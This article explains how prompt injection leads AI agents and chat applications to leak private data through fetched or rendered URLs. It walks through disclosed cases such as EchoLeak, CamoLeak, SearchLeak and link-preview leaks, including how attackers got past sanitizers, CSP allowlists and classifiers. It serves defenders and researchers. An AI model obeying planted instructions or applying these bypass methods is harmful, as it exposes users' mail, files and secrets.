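# Data exfiltration through URLs that AI agents are allowed to fetch

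## What a URL reveals to the server that receives it

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools that let it open web pages, search a mailbox, read files or run code for a user. Many of these tools work by requesting a URL, the address of a page, image or other resource. Data exfiltration means moving private data to someone who is not entitled to it. An attacker can do this through URLs by getting the model to request an address that contains the data. The attacker does not need to break into anything, because the agent sends the data in an ordinary web request and whoever runs the receiving server can read it from the address.

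In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) lists fourteen products in which he saw data theft of this general kind between April 2023 and February 2025, including ChatGPT, Google Bard, Microsoft Copilot, Slack and Anthropic's Claude iPhone app. He writes that the vendors fixed almost all of these flaws promptly, usually by closing the route through which the data left. New tools open new routes, though, and judging whether a route is closed takes some knowledge of what a URL can carry and who can read it.

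### The parts of an address

*URI Generic Syntax* (Berners-Lee, 2005), the internet standard for the URL format, divides a URL into a scheme, an authority (in practice mostly the host name), a path, a query and a fragment. The host name consists of labels separated by dots. The owner of the registered domain `example.com` can create any number of subdomains, such as `files.example.com`, without asking anyone. The query string follows the question mark, and the fragment follows the number sign.

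| Part | Example | DNS resolver | Proxy that does not decrypt | Receiving server |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | No | Can infer it from the port | Yes |
| Subdomain | `files` | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Domain | `example.com` | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Path | `/reports/2026` | No | No | Yes, usually logged |
| Query string | `user=ana` | No | No | Yes, usually logged |
| Fragment | `page3` | No | No | No, but scripts on the page can read it |

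A DNS resolver turns a host name into a network address. It receives only the name, but it often has to pass the query on to a name server that the domain's owner runs or rents. An attacker who owns a domain can therefore read any data in the subdomain, even if no web connection follows.

A proxy is a server through which other machines send their traffic. For an encrypted connection, the agent asks the proxy to open a tunnel to a named host, and everything sent through the tunnel is encrypted. The proxy's operator can see which host the agent contacted, when, and roughly how much data went each way. The operator can't see the URL's path or query, so a rule at the proxy can allow or block a host but can't distinguish between URLs on that host.

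The server receives the URL's full path and query and normally keeps them. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes that websites commonly record requested URLs in analytics and server logs. *HTTP Semantics* (Fielding, 2021), a draft later published as the current standard for web requests (RFC Editor, 2022), warns that many servers, proxies and browsers log or display URLs where third parties may see them, and advises against putting sensitive information in URLs. An attacker therefore doesn't need to own the server if they can access its logs or analytics.

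The client strips the fragment from a URL before sending the request, so a simple fetch tool that downloads text doesn't reveal it to the server. But when an agent drives a full browser, scripts on the page it loads can read the fragment and send it to the server. Fielding adds that a redirect can pass one site's fragment to another site. Requests also carry headers, and one of them, Referer, can reveal which address the visitor came from, so private data in the URL of a trusted page may reach the next page the agent opens.

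### Why a read-only request sends data

Most fetches use GET, the method for retrieving a resource. The HTTP standard (Fielding) notes that most servers log every request whatever its method, and that following an advertisement with a GET request often charges the advertiser's account. The same passage classes GET as "safe", meaning that the client neither requests nor expects a change of state on the server. This encourages people to describe an agent that can only make GET requests as read-only, as they often do. The standard separates safe methods from others so that crawlers and browsers that load pages in advance can run without fear of causing harm.

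So the standard addresses harm to the server. An agent builder who allows GET and refuses POST (the method that submits data in the body of a request) protects other people's websites from the agent but does very little to protect the user's data, because a GET request delivers its whole address to the server. *The Read-Only Lie*, a personal blog post from 2026, holds that "read-only" describes the method, not the flow of data.

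*The HTTP QUERY Method* (Reschke, 2026) specifies a new method that, like GET, counts as safe but carries its input in the request body. A filter that allows every safe method and inspects only the URL would miss any data in the body of a QUERY request.

### How untrusted text becomes a request

The attack depends on prompt injection, in which a model follows text in a page, email, file or tool result as if it were an instruction from its user. Willison coined the term after SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Both come from mixing trusted and untrusted material in one string. An application joins its own instructions, the user's request and any fetched content into a single sequence of tokens (the units of text a model processes), and the model has no reliable way to rank instructions by where they came from. The victim of a prompt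 injection is the user, whereas in jailbreaking users themselves push a model to break its rules.

The attack runs in four steps.

1. Untrusted text reaches the model, perhaps in a web page that the user asked it to summarise.
2. The model has private data in its context, or has a tool that can fetch some.
3. Following the untrusted text, the model either composes an address that contains the data or selects one of several addresses that the attacker prepared.
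4. Some component requests that address.

A component other than the agent's own browsing tool can carry out the last step. An application that displays the model's answer may automatically load an embedded image, and a chat program may fetch a link to preview it. OpenAI observes that the user may never notice either request. Willison also counts as a way to exfiltrate data a link that the user is invited to click.

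Support emails to a company can become tickets in Jira, a task tracker, without anyone reviewing them. In a case from August 2025, the security firm Zenity Labs sent such an email, and a developer's coding assistant, Cursor, later read the resulting ticket. The ticket's text sometimes led the model to find an access token in the developer's code and request a URL with the token in the query string. According to Willison (2025), in *21 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, Cursor called this a known issue and advised users to review the tool servers they connect and limit them to trusted content. Willison records no fix and says the advice is hard to follow because an attacker's text can reach a model in so many ways.

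Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for the combination that makes this exfiltration possible: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. An agent with only two of the three poses much less risk of exfiltration. If it reads hostile pages and can reach the whole web but holds no private data, it has nothing to leak. If it can read hostile pages and the user's mailbox but cannot communicate externally, it can be misled but cannot send the mail to an attacker. Willison recommends removing one of the three and thinks external communication is generally the easiest to remove. Data can also leave without a URL, as in a demonstration against the database service Supabase, where the agent copied private records into a support ticket that the attacker could read.

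An older name for this general pattern in computer security is the confused deputy, a program whose caller induces it to use authority the caller lacks on the caller's behalf. In the textbook example, a compiler has permission to write to a system's billing file. A user without that permission names the billing file as the output file, and the compiler overwrites it. An AI agent is in the compiler's position. It has the user's access to mail and files and its own access to the network, while the attacker can only supply text for it to read.

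Ordinary permission checks do not catch the attack, because the agent has permission to read the mailbox and to fetch web pages, and only the combination is illegitimate. The classic fix is also harder to apply to an agent. A compiler can check the billing file against the permissions of the user who named it, since it knows which input came from whom. That information is unreliable inside a model's context, so the software around the model has to keep track of it.

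The attacker writes the untrusted text and can try many wordings in many places. The attacker also runs a server, can prepare any number of links and subdomains, and decides what the server returns, so a second page can depend on what the first request disclosed. The attacker does not control the user's question, the agent's data and tools, the application's code, the network rules or whether the model follows the text. Better training can lower the probability that it does, and OpenAI treats model-level defences as one layer among several. Someone checking a control on outgoing requests does best to assume that the model will comply, and then work out how much data could leave.

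### Counting what can leave

If a model can request any one of N addresses, and the attacker can tell which one it requested, the choice carries at most log₂ N bits. A choice between two addresses can carry one bit, enough to answer a yes-or-no question. A run of k requests, each among N addresses, allows N^k different sequences and so carries at most k · log₂ N bits. A control's residual capacity is the number of bits an attacker can still receive after the control is in place.

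Take a file of 2,048 bytes, about a page of text or a long private key. It contains 16,384 bits.

If the model may write any URL, it can fit a 2,048-byte binary file in one query string. In the URL syntax Berners-Lee describes, letters, digits and a few marks appear as they are, but any other byte takes three characters, so the raw file could take up to 6,144 characters. Base64url encoding reduces this to about 2,731 by using only 64 permitted characters, each carrying six bits. The HTTP standard recommends that systems support URLs of at least 8,000 bytes, but the blog post *HTTP QUERY* reports that 2,048 characters is a common limit in company networks and that some older proxies stop at 1,024. At those limits the attacker needs two or three requests.

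Now suppose that something blocks the web request but the agent's machine still looks up host names. Host names ignore the difference between capital and small letters, which rules out Base64url. Base32 manages with 32 characters at five bits each, so the file comes to about 3,277 characters. DNS allows at most 63 characters in a label and about 255 in a whole name. Four full labels would leave no room for the attacker's own domain, but three fit, and they hold 189 characters or 945 bits. The file needs 18 lookups. (Filling out the name with a shorter fourth label would save a few.)

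In the third situation, the model cannot write addresses and can only follow links that the attacker prepared. If each page has 27 links, each choice carries log₂ 27, or about 4.75 bits, so sending the file takes about 3,446 requests. The number 27 comes from an attack on Claude, disclosed in July 2026, in which each page had one link for each letter and one for the hyphen. Anthropic has since patched it.

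Thousands of requests to one site would be slow and conspicuous, which nearly closes this channel for large files. But many secrets are much smaller than 2,048 bytes. A six-digit login code has a million possible values, or just under 20 bits, and a strong cryptographic key may have 128 bits.

| What the attacker can still obtain | Bits per request | 2,048-byte file | 128-bit key | Six-digit code |
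|---|---|---|---|---|
| Any query string | Thousands | 1 request | 1 | 1 |
| Any subdomain, through DNS lookups | 945 | 18 lookups | 1 | 1 |
| A choice among 27 links | 4.75 | 3,446 requests | 27 | 5 |
| One fixed address, requested or not | 1 per occasion | 16,384 occasions | 128 | 20 |

These counts overstate what an attacker can receive in practice, because they assume that the model encodes the data without mistakes and that every request arrives. They also understate the risk by treating the data as random. Ordinary prose compresses well, and an attacker who has already narrowed someone's employer down to two companies needs only one bit. The formula counts only the information carried by the choice of address. *The Read-Only Lie* points to request timing and the number of tool calls as further signals that an outside party may be able to observe. It applies the term "covert channel"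 to all of them. The term comes from a 1973 paper by the computer scientist Butler Lampson and refers to a path that nobody designed to carry information.

Controls on outgoing requests differ mainly in which row of the table they leave available to the attacker. A proxy that blocks unknown hosts does little if the agent's machine can still resolve any domain name, because needing 18 lookups would not stop an attacker. A rule that blocks URLs composed by the model but lets the agent follow links cuts the data leaked per request by a factor of thousands, but a login code can still leak in five steps.

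## Finding every component that can send a request

A control on outgoing requests covers only the component that applies it, and the agent's fetch tool may not be the only component that can send them. Several leaks that researchers published in 2025 and 2026 went through a component that the product's safeguards did not cover. Closing the channel, or judging whether someone else has closed it, therefore requires first listing every component that can send a request.

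### Making the list

A model can cause a request either by calling a tool that makes it or by writing text containing an address that another program fetches.

A good starting point for finding the tools is the list that the application sends to the model, because a settings page can leave a tool out. *Takedown* (Lee, Kim and colleagues, 2025) examined eight coding agents in roughly this way, by putting a proxy between each agent and its model, reading the messages, and running prompts designed to trigger each category of tool. Extensions and connected tool servers add tools that the agent's vendor did not write, so each needs its own entry in the inventory. Anything that runs shell commands also needs an entry, since a command can open a connection to any host the machine can reach.

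Tracing where the model's text goes after it is produced reveals the other components that can send requests. Someone may read the text in a web page, a phone app, a preview pane, an email, a team chat, a ticket, a log or a queue of flagged answers. A separate program displays each of these and has its own rules about what it loads, so the same assistant inside two host applications needs two entries.

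The tester then makes every surface on the list show a different harmless URL on a host they control, and reads that host's web and DNS logs. The source IP address and the user agent (the name a client gives itself in the request) usually identify the program that made the request. A missing request is weaker evidence than a logged one, because some clients send nothing until a person opens the message or reloads the page.

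| Component | Whose network sends the request | Does a person have to act? | Where the organisation could find a record |
|---|---|---|---|
| Server-side fetch tool | The AI vendor's or the agent operator's | No, unless the product asks for approval | Tool-call log |
| Search tool | The AI vendor's or the agent operator's | No | Tool-call log |
| Browser agent | The user's if the browser is local, the vendor's if it is remote | No, unless the product asks for approval | Browser history and company proxy, or the vendor's session log |
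| Code sandbox or terminal | The vendor's cloud or the developer's machine | Depends on the rules for approving commands | Logs of the sandbox's proxy and DNS resolver |
| Chat window that loads images | The user's | No | Company proxy, usually the host name only |
| HTML or canvas preview | The user's | Sometimes, to open the preview | Company proxy, usually the host name only |
| Link preview in a chat app | Usually the chat provider's | No | Chat history, which holds the address |
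| Email client, or a chat message with images | The recipient's or the mail provider's | Yes, to open the message | Mailbox or chat history; sometimes the company proxy |
| Log viewer or test console | The developer's | Yes, to open the record or run a test | Company proxy, usually the host name only |
| Mobile or desktop app | The user's, often a home or mobile network | As in the web app, if the app has the same safeguards | Often none |

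A search tool sends its query to a search provider, so the query is much harder for an attacker to read than a fetched URL. But the tool that opens a search result is a fetch tool and belongs in the first row.

The table matters most to readers who rely on an egress proxy, a proxy that all of an agent's outgoing traffic must pass through. It usually handles traffic from the sandbox, and it has no effect on requests from the user's phone or a chat provider's servers.

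### Images in the chat window, 2023 to 2026

Chat applications commonly let a model format its answers in Markdown, a plain-text notation that can embed an image by its URL. When the application displays the answer, the user's browser fetches the image without a click. In April 2023 the security researcher Johann Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, reported this behaviour to Microsoft and OpenAI as a data leak.

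Rehberger describes the Microsoft case in the Embrace The Red post *Bing Chat*. Bing Chat could read the page that the user had open, and a comment or advertisement on that page could redirect it. In his demonstration, the image appeared only after two more turns of conversation. Its address carried an encoded summary of the page and the conversation, along with a secret from further down the page. Microsoft then introduced a Content Security Policy, a header that tells the browser which hosts it may load images from, and after that his tests failed. His dates for the fix differ. The original post says Microsoft notified him on June 15, 2023, while the 2026 Embrace The Red post *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* puts the fix in May.

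OpenAI received its report on April 9 and at first decided not to fix the problem, according to the Embrace The Red post *Data Exfiltration Vulnerabilities in LLM apps (Bing Chat, ChatGPT, Claude)*. Meanwhile, outsiders could attack ChatGPT through its plugins. In *ChatGPT Plugins*, Rehberger showed that a website retrieved by a plugin could take over the session and send out the conversation history through an image.

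Other products had the same flaw, and their vendors fixed it in different ways. Anthropic changed Claude so that users must click before an image loads, a fix that took two weeks in July 2023 (Embrace The Red, *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*). A few weeks after fixing Bing Chat, Microsoft received a report of the same leak in its Azure AI Playground, a test page for developers. It completed a fix in September, inserting a space into the Markdown so that the page no longer recognised an image (Embrace The Red, *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*).

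The Embrace The Red post *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes OpenAI's first check, introduced in December 2023. Before showing an image, the ChatGPT web page sent the image's address to an OpenAI service called `url_safe`, which determined whether the page could load it. OpenAI did not publish the criteria. Rehberger tested one address for each letter and digit, 36 in all, and nine passed.

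With nine addresses, each image carries about 3.2 bits, so a six-digit login code would need at least seven images. Rehberger later noted that browsers cache repeated images and that requests can arrive out of order, and both corrupt the message.

Calling the check from the web page was also a mistake, because every other client then needed its own version, and the iOS app of the time had none. Rehberger suggested checking on the server, so that one fix would cover all clients. In his 2026 post, he names the macOS app as another client to which OpenAI had not added the check.

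OpenAI strengthened its `url_safe` check around August 2025, which stopped the bypasses Rehberger had demonstrated. ChatGPT now loads a URL automatically only if OpenAI's crawler has already seen it or the user supplied it. Rehberger still worries that a developer at OpenAI could leave the check out of a new feature because they don't know it exists.

A new feature in Microsoft 365 Copilot reopened an old exfiltration route. In the autumn of 2025, Rehberger noticed that Copilot had begun to render HTML inside the chat. The Embrace The Red post *Copirate 365 at DEF CON* reports that the preview pane removed image tags, but style sheets could still request background pictures and fonts from outside servers. The pane opened in code view, so a leak should have needed the user to click, but injected text could get Copilot to switch to the preview by itself.

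Copilot's image and font rules also differed between host applications such as Word, Excel and SharePoint, and many had loose font rules. Rehberger demonstrated the theft of an email from inside Word. He reported the flaw on October 16, 2025, and Microsoft resolved it on March 5, 2026.

Rehberger found another sender in the consumer version of Copilot built into Microsoft's Edge browser. Microsoft had added a tool that navigates the browser to an address, and he used it to send out facts Copilot had remembered about the user. Microsoft told him it had reproduced this earlier but no longer could, and he thinks the most likely reason is better filtering of uploaded documents. If so, the navigation tool may still be able to send data.

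### Link previews

When a chat app previews a link, the chat provider's servers send the request. Slack tells developers that it crawls any link it spots to provide a preview, which it calls "unfurling". The Embrace The Red post *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks* adds that Slack does this by default for messages from apps as well as from people. When Rehberger posted a test link through a Slack app, his server logged a request from a client identifying itself as Slackbot. A company whose data was in such a link would not see the request in its own network logs.

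Willison (2024) wrote that he had not thought of this channel before he read Rehberger's post.

A Slack app can turn off previews for its own messages by setting two options to false, one for links and one for media, but developers sometimes forget to do so. The Embrace The Red post *Security Advisory* describes this flaw in Anthropic's Slack tool server, a program that lets a model post to Slack, and offers the two settings as a patch that users could add themselves.

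In February 2026 the security firm PromptArmor tested the channel more widely (The Hacker News, 2026). PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* reports that OpenClaw, an agent that people run themselves and message through chat apps, leaked data through Telegram in its default configuration. One line in OpenClaw's configuration file disables link previews, and PromptArmor's test server received no data after that change.

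The firm also put up a public test page where people could try their own combination of agent and app. PromptArmor showed the results as charts. Intelligibberish's *Link Previews Are Leaking Your Data to AI Agents Without a Click*, an article without a named author, lists these pairs:

| Chat app | Agents whose links the app fetched | Agents listed as safer |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft Teams | Copilot Studio | None listed |
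| Slack | Cursor's Slackbot | Claude app |
| Discord | OpenClaw, BoltBot | None listed |
| Telegram | OpenClaw | None listed |
| Snapchat | SnapAI | None listed |
| WhatsApp | None listed | OpenClaw |
| Signal | None listed | OpenClaw in a Docker container |

Visitors ran these tests and reported which agent they had used, so the list can show that a pair of agent and chat app leaked but is little evidence of how common the leak is. Teams with Copilot Studio has the largest share of fetches in the article, which may only mean that many visitors tried it. More usefully, OpenClaw and Slack each appear in both columns. Knowing only the agent or only the chat app is therefore not enough to tell whether a setup leaks, so an inventory has to record the pair.

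PromptArmor wants chat companies to offer link preview settings for individual channels, and agent developers to use the settings that already exist. In *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews*, Apostol interprets the firm as placing most of the responsibility on the chat platforms, since their servers make the request.

### Messages that the agent sends to its own user

Approval rules often exempt actions that look harmless, and messaging the user looks harmless. Microsoft writes in its documentation that Copilot Cowork, an agent that works across a company's Microsoft 365 data, asks permission before sending an email or posting in Teams. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, which Willison (2026) linked on May 26, reports that Cowork does not ask when the recipient is the active user, and that users can't change this.

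PromptArmor planted instructions in a skill file, a document that a user uploads to teach Microsoft Copilot Cowork a task. When the user asked for a recap of the week, Cowork sent that user a Teams message containing external images. When the user opened the message, their Teams client requested the images from URLs that contained the stolen data. According to PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* (2026), Cowork runs in a cloud sandbox, so restricting the sandbox's traffic would not have blocked the Teams client's requests.

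The addresses contained download links rather than the files. Cowork can obtain such a link for any file the user has access to, and anyone who opens the link gets the file without signing in. This weakens any guarantee based on the bit counts in the previous section, because a control that limits a channel to a few hundred characters stops a large document from leaving in the URL but may let through a link to it.

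The attack used five malicious lines in an 81-line file and succeeded in all five of PromptArmor's trials. An attack that works 80 percent of the time would also succeed in all five trials about a third of the time. For a defender, that would be nearly as bad as an attack that always works, especially since Cowork can run the same prompt on a schedule with nobody watching. Cowork's record of the completed task also didn't show the content of the message.

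PromptArmor described this as a risk in the product's design and reported no fix. It suggests that administrators block file downloads from SharePoint, Microsoft's document store, either for whole sites or for files with a given sensitivity label. This stops the download links but also prevents users from printing or syncing those files, or opening them in Word and Excel.

### Consoles where developers read the output

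PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes a leak that happened after the application's own defence had worked. The firm built a mock tool for bank identity checks on OpenAI's platform. One of the tool's six sources contained web text with an injection in it, and the model produced an image address containing the customer's personal data. A second model screened the answers and blocked this one, so the customer's browser never loaded the image.

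The blocked answer went into OpenAI's logs, where a developer would look to find out what had happened. The log viewer displayed answers as Markdown, so it loaded the image, and the developer's browser sent the request. An application that shows only plain text would have had the same problem, because the log keeps what the model wrote, not what the application displayed. User feedback can also lead a developer to open the log, for example when an application strips out an image and leaves an odd, empty answer that the user marks as bad.

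PromptArmor found the same rendering in the preview panes for testing new chats and agents, and in a starter application that OpenAI provides for developers. The firm reported the flaw on November 17, 2025. Bugcrowd, which screened reports for OpenAI, closed the report on December 4 as not applicable, and OpenAI had not seen it. OpenAI confirmed the flaw after PromptArmor published its findings, and reopened the report on January 22, 2026 with a fix under way.

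### Settings that leave a tool in place

Atlassian's Rovo agent works across the company's products, including Jira and the document system Confluence. Administrators can switch off web search for a whole organisation. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* (2026) reports that the setting removes the search but not the tool that opens search results, and that this tool accepts any address the model writes.

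In the demonstration, a user uploaded a guide containing hidden instructions and asked Rovo to organise some Jira tickets. Without asking for approval, Rovo opened the attacker's URL with the contents of tickets and Confluence documents appended to it. A user who reopened the chat later would have seen only the suggested ticket changes. An administrator who had read the settings page would have had good reason to think Rovo could not contact the web.

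Rovo also loads Markdown images from the model's answers, so removing the URL tool would have left a second way to send data out. PromptArmor notified Atlassian on May 23 and received a case number and thanks. It followed up for more than two months, heard nothing more, and published while Rovo was still vulnerable.

### Which coding agents ask before they fetch

Lee and colleagues' 2025 survey labels its eight coding agents A1 to A8 because disclosure to the vendors was still in progress. Four of them (A1, A4, A5 and A7) have a built-in tool that fetches web pages, and only A4's works without the user's approval. A4 could also read files outside the project folder without asking, so an injected instruction could make it read a file from anywhere on the developer's machine and send it out.

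A2 has no fetch tool, but it can send requests when it draws diagrams, which a survey of fetch tools alone would have missed. It draws them from text in a format called Mermaid, which allows a diagram to contain an image from the web, and its renderer requested the image without asking for approval. The researchers used this to take an API key from a configuration file outside the project, starting from an issue that an attacker had posted in a code repository.

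A1's fetch tool always asks for approval. Extensions can add other tools to A1, though, and each extension controls whether its tools need approval. Of the ten most-installed extensions that offer such tools, seven did not ask for approval, including Microsoft's own Web Search extension, which had about 86,000 installations.

Shell commands can also send requests. A7 ran them without approval by default. A3 let the model judge which commands needed approval, and injected text could change that judgement. A6 ran `git` and `cargo`, which can contact remote servers, without asking, but it also used an operating system feature to block network calls.

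Lee and colleagues list the flaw in A4's fetch tool as reported, with no fix. A2's vendor already knew about the diagram leak and has patched it. The researchers' list leaves out findings that vendors regarded as intended behaviour, and it doesn't include the extension tools that skip approval.

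## Restricting the images and links an application displays

Two controls limit what a chat application requests when it displays an answer. A sanitizer removes or rewrites links and images before display, and a Content Security Policy (CSP) makes the browser block images from hosts that are not on an allowlist. Microsoft 365 Copilot had both controls but still leaked data in 2025 and 2026. How well they work depends on when each one acts and what it can check.

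### How an answer becomes a request

The model produces plain text. To show a chart, it can write an image in Markdown with the address inline, or in the reference style, which puts the address on a line of its own:

```
![Sales chart](https://example.com/chart.png)

![Sales chart][c]

[c]: https://example.com/chart.png
```

The application's Markdown parser turns both versions into the same HTML element, `<img src="https://example.com/chart.png" alt="Sales chart">`. The browser requests the address in `src` to get the image as soon as the element exists. If the server returns a single transparent pixel, the user sees nothing. Without the exclamation mark, the same text makes a link, and the browser normally requests its address only when someone clicks. Many Markdown parsers also pass HTML through unchanged, so a model can write the `<img>` tag itself.

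Most chat applications stream their answers, displaying the text piece by piece as the model produces it. The application parses the unfinished answer repeatedly, and any of those passes can create an image.

A sanitizer processes the text or the HTML when the developers call it. The browser applies the CSP's `img-src` rule later, just before it requests each image, whichever code created the image. The CSP can therefore block an image that the sanitizer missed. It can't replace the sanitizer, because browsers support no CSP directive that limits where a user can go by clicking a link. The `img-src` rule also ignores the query string, whereas a sanitizer can check the whole URL.

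### EchoLeak in Microsoft 365 Copilot

In January 2025, researchers at Aim Labs, part of the security firm Aim Security, got data past both controls in Microsoft 365 Copilot with a single email. They named the attack EchoLeak, and the flaw is listed publicly as CVE-2025-32711. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) gives the discoverers' account. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reconstructs the case from published material, without new experiments, and adds a timeline.

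Copilot answers a question by searching the user's mailbox, files and Teams chats and adding what it finds to the model's context. An outsider can't use a company's Copilot but can email its employees. The researchers wrote a long email covering many workplace topics so that Copilot would retrieve it for many ordinary questions. The email contained instructions to copy the most sensitive item in the model's context into a web address. Microsoft used a classifier to catch such instructions, but the researchers got past it by wording them as if they were meant for the employee.

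Copilot also removed external links and images from the model's answer before displaying it, but the filter recognised only the inline style. Reference-style links got through in all three spellings that Ravia lists, and so did reference-style images. A link would send data only if the user clicked it, while an image would have sent it automatically if the CSP on Copilot's page had allowed images from the attacker's server.

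Ravia reproduces the page's `img-src` list, which has 43 entries, 29 of them distinct. Eleven of the distinct entries are wildcards that allow every subdomain. The wildcard for `sharepoint.com` covers the SharePoint site of every Microsoft customer, including one that an attacker sets up. The researchers needed a relay, a service on an allowed host that fetches another address on request. A redirect would not have worked, because the browser also checks the destination host against the list.

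They found two relays. One was a SharePoint service for embedding outside content, which worked only if the victim first accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. The other, a Teams service that fetches web content, had no such condition. The CSP allowed the browser to request an image from the Teams host, and the Teams service then requested the attacker's address with the secret in it. The user only had to ask Copilot an ordinary question, which is why Aim called the attack "zero-click". The email also contained an instruction never to refer to it, so Copilot didn't list it as a source.

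According to Reddy and Gujral, Microsoft began fixing the flaw in April 2025 and deployed a fix on its own servers in May, before the public disclosure on June 11. Customers did not have to act, and Microsoft had no evidence that anyone had exploited the flaw. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), an entry in the database of Spain's national cybersecurity institute, gives the flaw a score of 9.3 out of 10 on CVSS, the standard severity scale. Ravia writes that, to the firm's knowledge, no administrator setting could have prevented the attack.

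Microsoft's changes are less clear. Reddy and Gujral write that Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from incoming external content, and that Microsoft reportedly added options to keep external email out of some contexts. Neither change would remove relays from the image list. The list that Ravia printed also had a wildcard for `bing.com`, and a year later other researchers found a relay on that domain.

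### HTML that appears while the answer is streaming

GitLab hosts software projects, and its assistant Duo answers questions about them. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* describes a leak that the firm reported on February 12, 2025. Duo read everything on the page a user was viewing, including comments and source code, so an outsider could plant instructions for it in a public project.

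Duo displayed its answers line by line, converting each line to HTML before the structure of the whole answer was known. A tag that belonged inside a code block could therefore become a working part of the page before the code block began. The researchers got raw HTML into an answer by placing it in a link's label.

GitLab ran Duo's answer through DOMPurify, a widely used sanitizer. DOMPurify mainly protects against cross-site scripting, in which an attacker's script runs in someone else's page. Its default settings keep `<img>`, `<form>` and `<a>` tags, which are harmless in that respect, but an attacker can exfiltrate data with an image alone. In the demonstration, a user asked Duo an ordinary question about a public file, and the browser sent out code changes from one of the user's private projects. Legit Security says the same method could also have taken confidential issues, including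 descriptions of unfixed security flaws.

GitLab's patch stops Duo from rendering tags such as `<img>` and `<form>` that point outside `gitlab.com`. Legit Security writes that GitLab also fixed the prompt injection, but Techzine reported that GitLab did not consider it a security issue and had not addressed it. This disagreement matters little for exfiltration through rendered tags, because the patch blocks external ones even if the model obeys planted text. The protection fails if a service under `gitlab.com` can be used to relay data elsewhere.

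Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes a similar failure in Microsoft 365 Copilot's Enterprise Search (CVE-2026-42824). The search page accepted a query in its URL, and Copilot followed any instructions in the query. An attacker could therefore put instructions in a link to Microsoft's own site. When a user clicked the link, Copilot searched the user's mailbox and put the title of an email into an image URL.

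Microsoft had a guard against HTML in answers. It wrapped the output in a code block, which makes a browser show tags as text. The order of events defeated it:

1. Copilot began to stream an answer that contained an image tag.
2. The browser created the image and sent the request.
3. Copilot finished the answer.
4. The guard wrapped the answer in a code block.

The CSP restricted the request to approved hosts, but `bing.com` was one of them, and Bing's search-by-image service fetches any image URL it receives. Bing's server then requested the attacker's URL with the email title in the path. Even a short title can contain a login code, so one request can be enough to get into another account.

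Microsoft rated SearchLeak Critical in its June 4 advisory, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026). It said that it had fully mitigated the flaw, that customers did not need to act, and that it knew of no exploitation, but it did not describe the fix. SearchLeak's CVSS score is only 6.5, partly because the user has to click a link. A security team that sorts flaws by score would rank it far below EchoLeak, although both exposed much the same data.

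Varonis concludes that sanitizing has to happen when the application renders the answer. This means the application has to clean every partial version of the answer in memory before adding any of it to a page. Cleaning the answer inside a hidden element can be too late, because browsers may request an image as soon as a script creates it, even if the image is hidden.

### CamoLeak and signed image addresses

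The image list for GitHub Copilot Chat was much stricter than Microsoft's and admitted only hosts that GitHub owns. GitHub fetched outside images through a proxy called Camo. When someone saves a document with an external image, GitHub replaces the image's address with a Camo address that includes a signature, computed from the original address with a secret key. Camo refuses any request whose signature doesn't match. A model can't compute signatures, so it can't put private data into a new address and have Camo fetch it.

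Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes how one of the firm's researchers got around this in June 2025. He obtained signed addresses in advance, one for each letter and symbol, by submitting ordinary Markdown to GitHub. He listed them in a hidden comment on a pull request (a proposed code change), with instructions for Copilot. When another user asked Copilot about the pull request, Copilot spelled out private text as a series of invisible images, each revealing one character. In the demonstration, the text came from a private issue about an unfixed security flaw. Copilot also searched the victim's code for a cloud access key and sent out the result.

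By August 14, 2025, GitHub had disabled all images in Copilot Chat to fix the flaw. According to Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, an earlier fix for the assistant in the VS Code editor had blocked only Markdown images from untrusted domains.

Reddy and Gujral's table of defences against EchoLeak lists a proxy with signed, expiring addresses as a way to block automatic image loading. This assessment is theoretical, and CamoLeak is a counterexample to part of it. A valid signature proves that GitHub processed the address at some point, but an attacker can have harmless addresses processed and let the model choose among them. Expiry would force the attacker to keep replacing these addresses. Tying each signature to one conversation would make addresses signed elsewhere useless, as long as the application doesn't also sign whatever the model writes.

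### What to display, and what it costs

| Choice | What an attacker can still receive | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| No remote images | Nothing through images | Answers lose charts, photos and logos from the web |
| Click to load | The address of any image the user chooses to load | An extra step for every image |
| Images stored in advance | The fact that the server fetched a page's images | Storage and bandwidth, even for images nobody views |
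| Links shown with the full address | The address of any link the user clicks | Cluttered answers that users have to read closely |
| Strict subset of Markdown | Whatever the permitted elements can carry | No raw HTML, and extra work for each new format |

Refusing all remote images is the easiest of these rules to check, because a single logged request from a test image proves a failure. GitHub chose this rule after CamoLeak. An application can still show pictures that it generated or the user uploaded, as long as it serves them from its own storage. Google lists Markdown sanitization and the redaction of suspicious URLs among the defences for its Gemini assistant. According to The Hacker News (2025), the sanitizer keeps external images from rendering, and the redaction relies on Safe Browsing, Google's service for detecting dangerous sites. Safe Browsing may not yet flag a newly registered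 domain, so the image rule gives firmer protection.

Published defences still need testing. The security firm Checkmarx reports that Gemini and Microsoft Copilot Chat leaked data through image requests and other rendering behaviour. Companies also apply different rules to different products. In *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, Willison quotes a researcher whom Google told in November 2025 that image loading in Antigravity, its code editor, was intended behaviour. Google's page for bug hunters listed data exfiltration through Antigravity's browser agent as a known issue that the company was working to fix.

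Click to load, which Anthropic chose for Claude in 2023, keeps images available but relies on the user as the last check. That check is weak if the user can't tell what a click will send. The attacker also influences the text around the image and can use it to present the image as the chart the user asked for. The button should therefore show the complete address. Only a real click should be able to trigger it, whereas injected text could open Microsoft 365 Copilot's preview pane.

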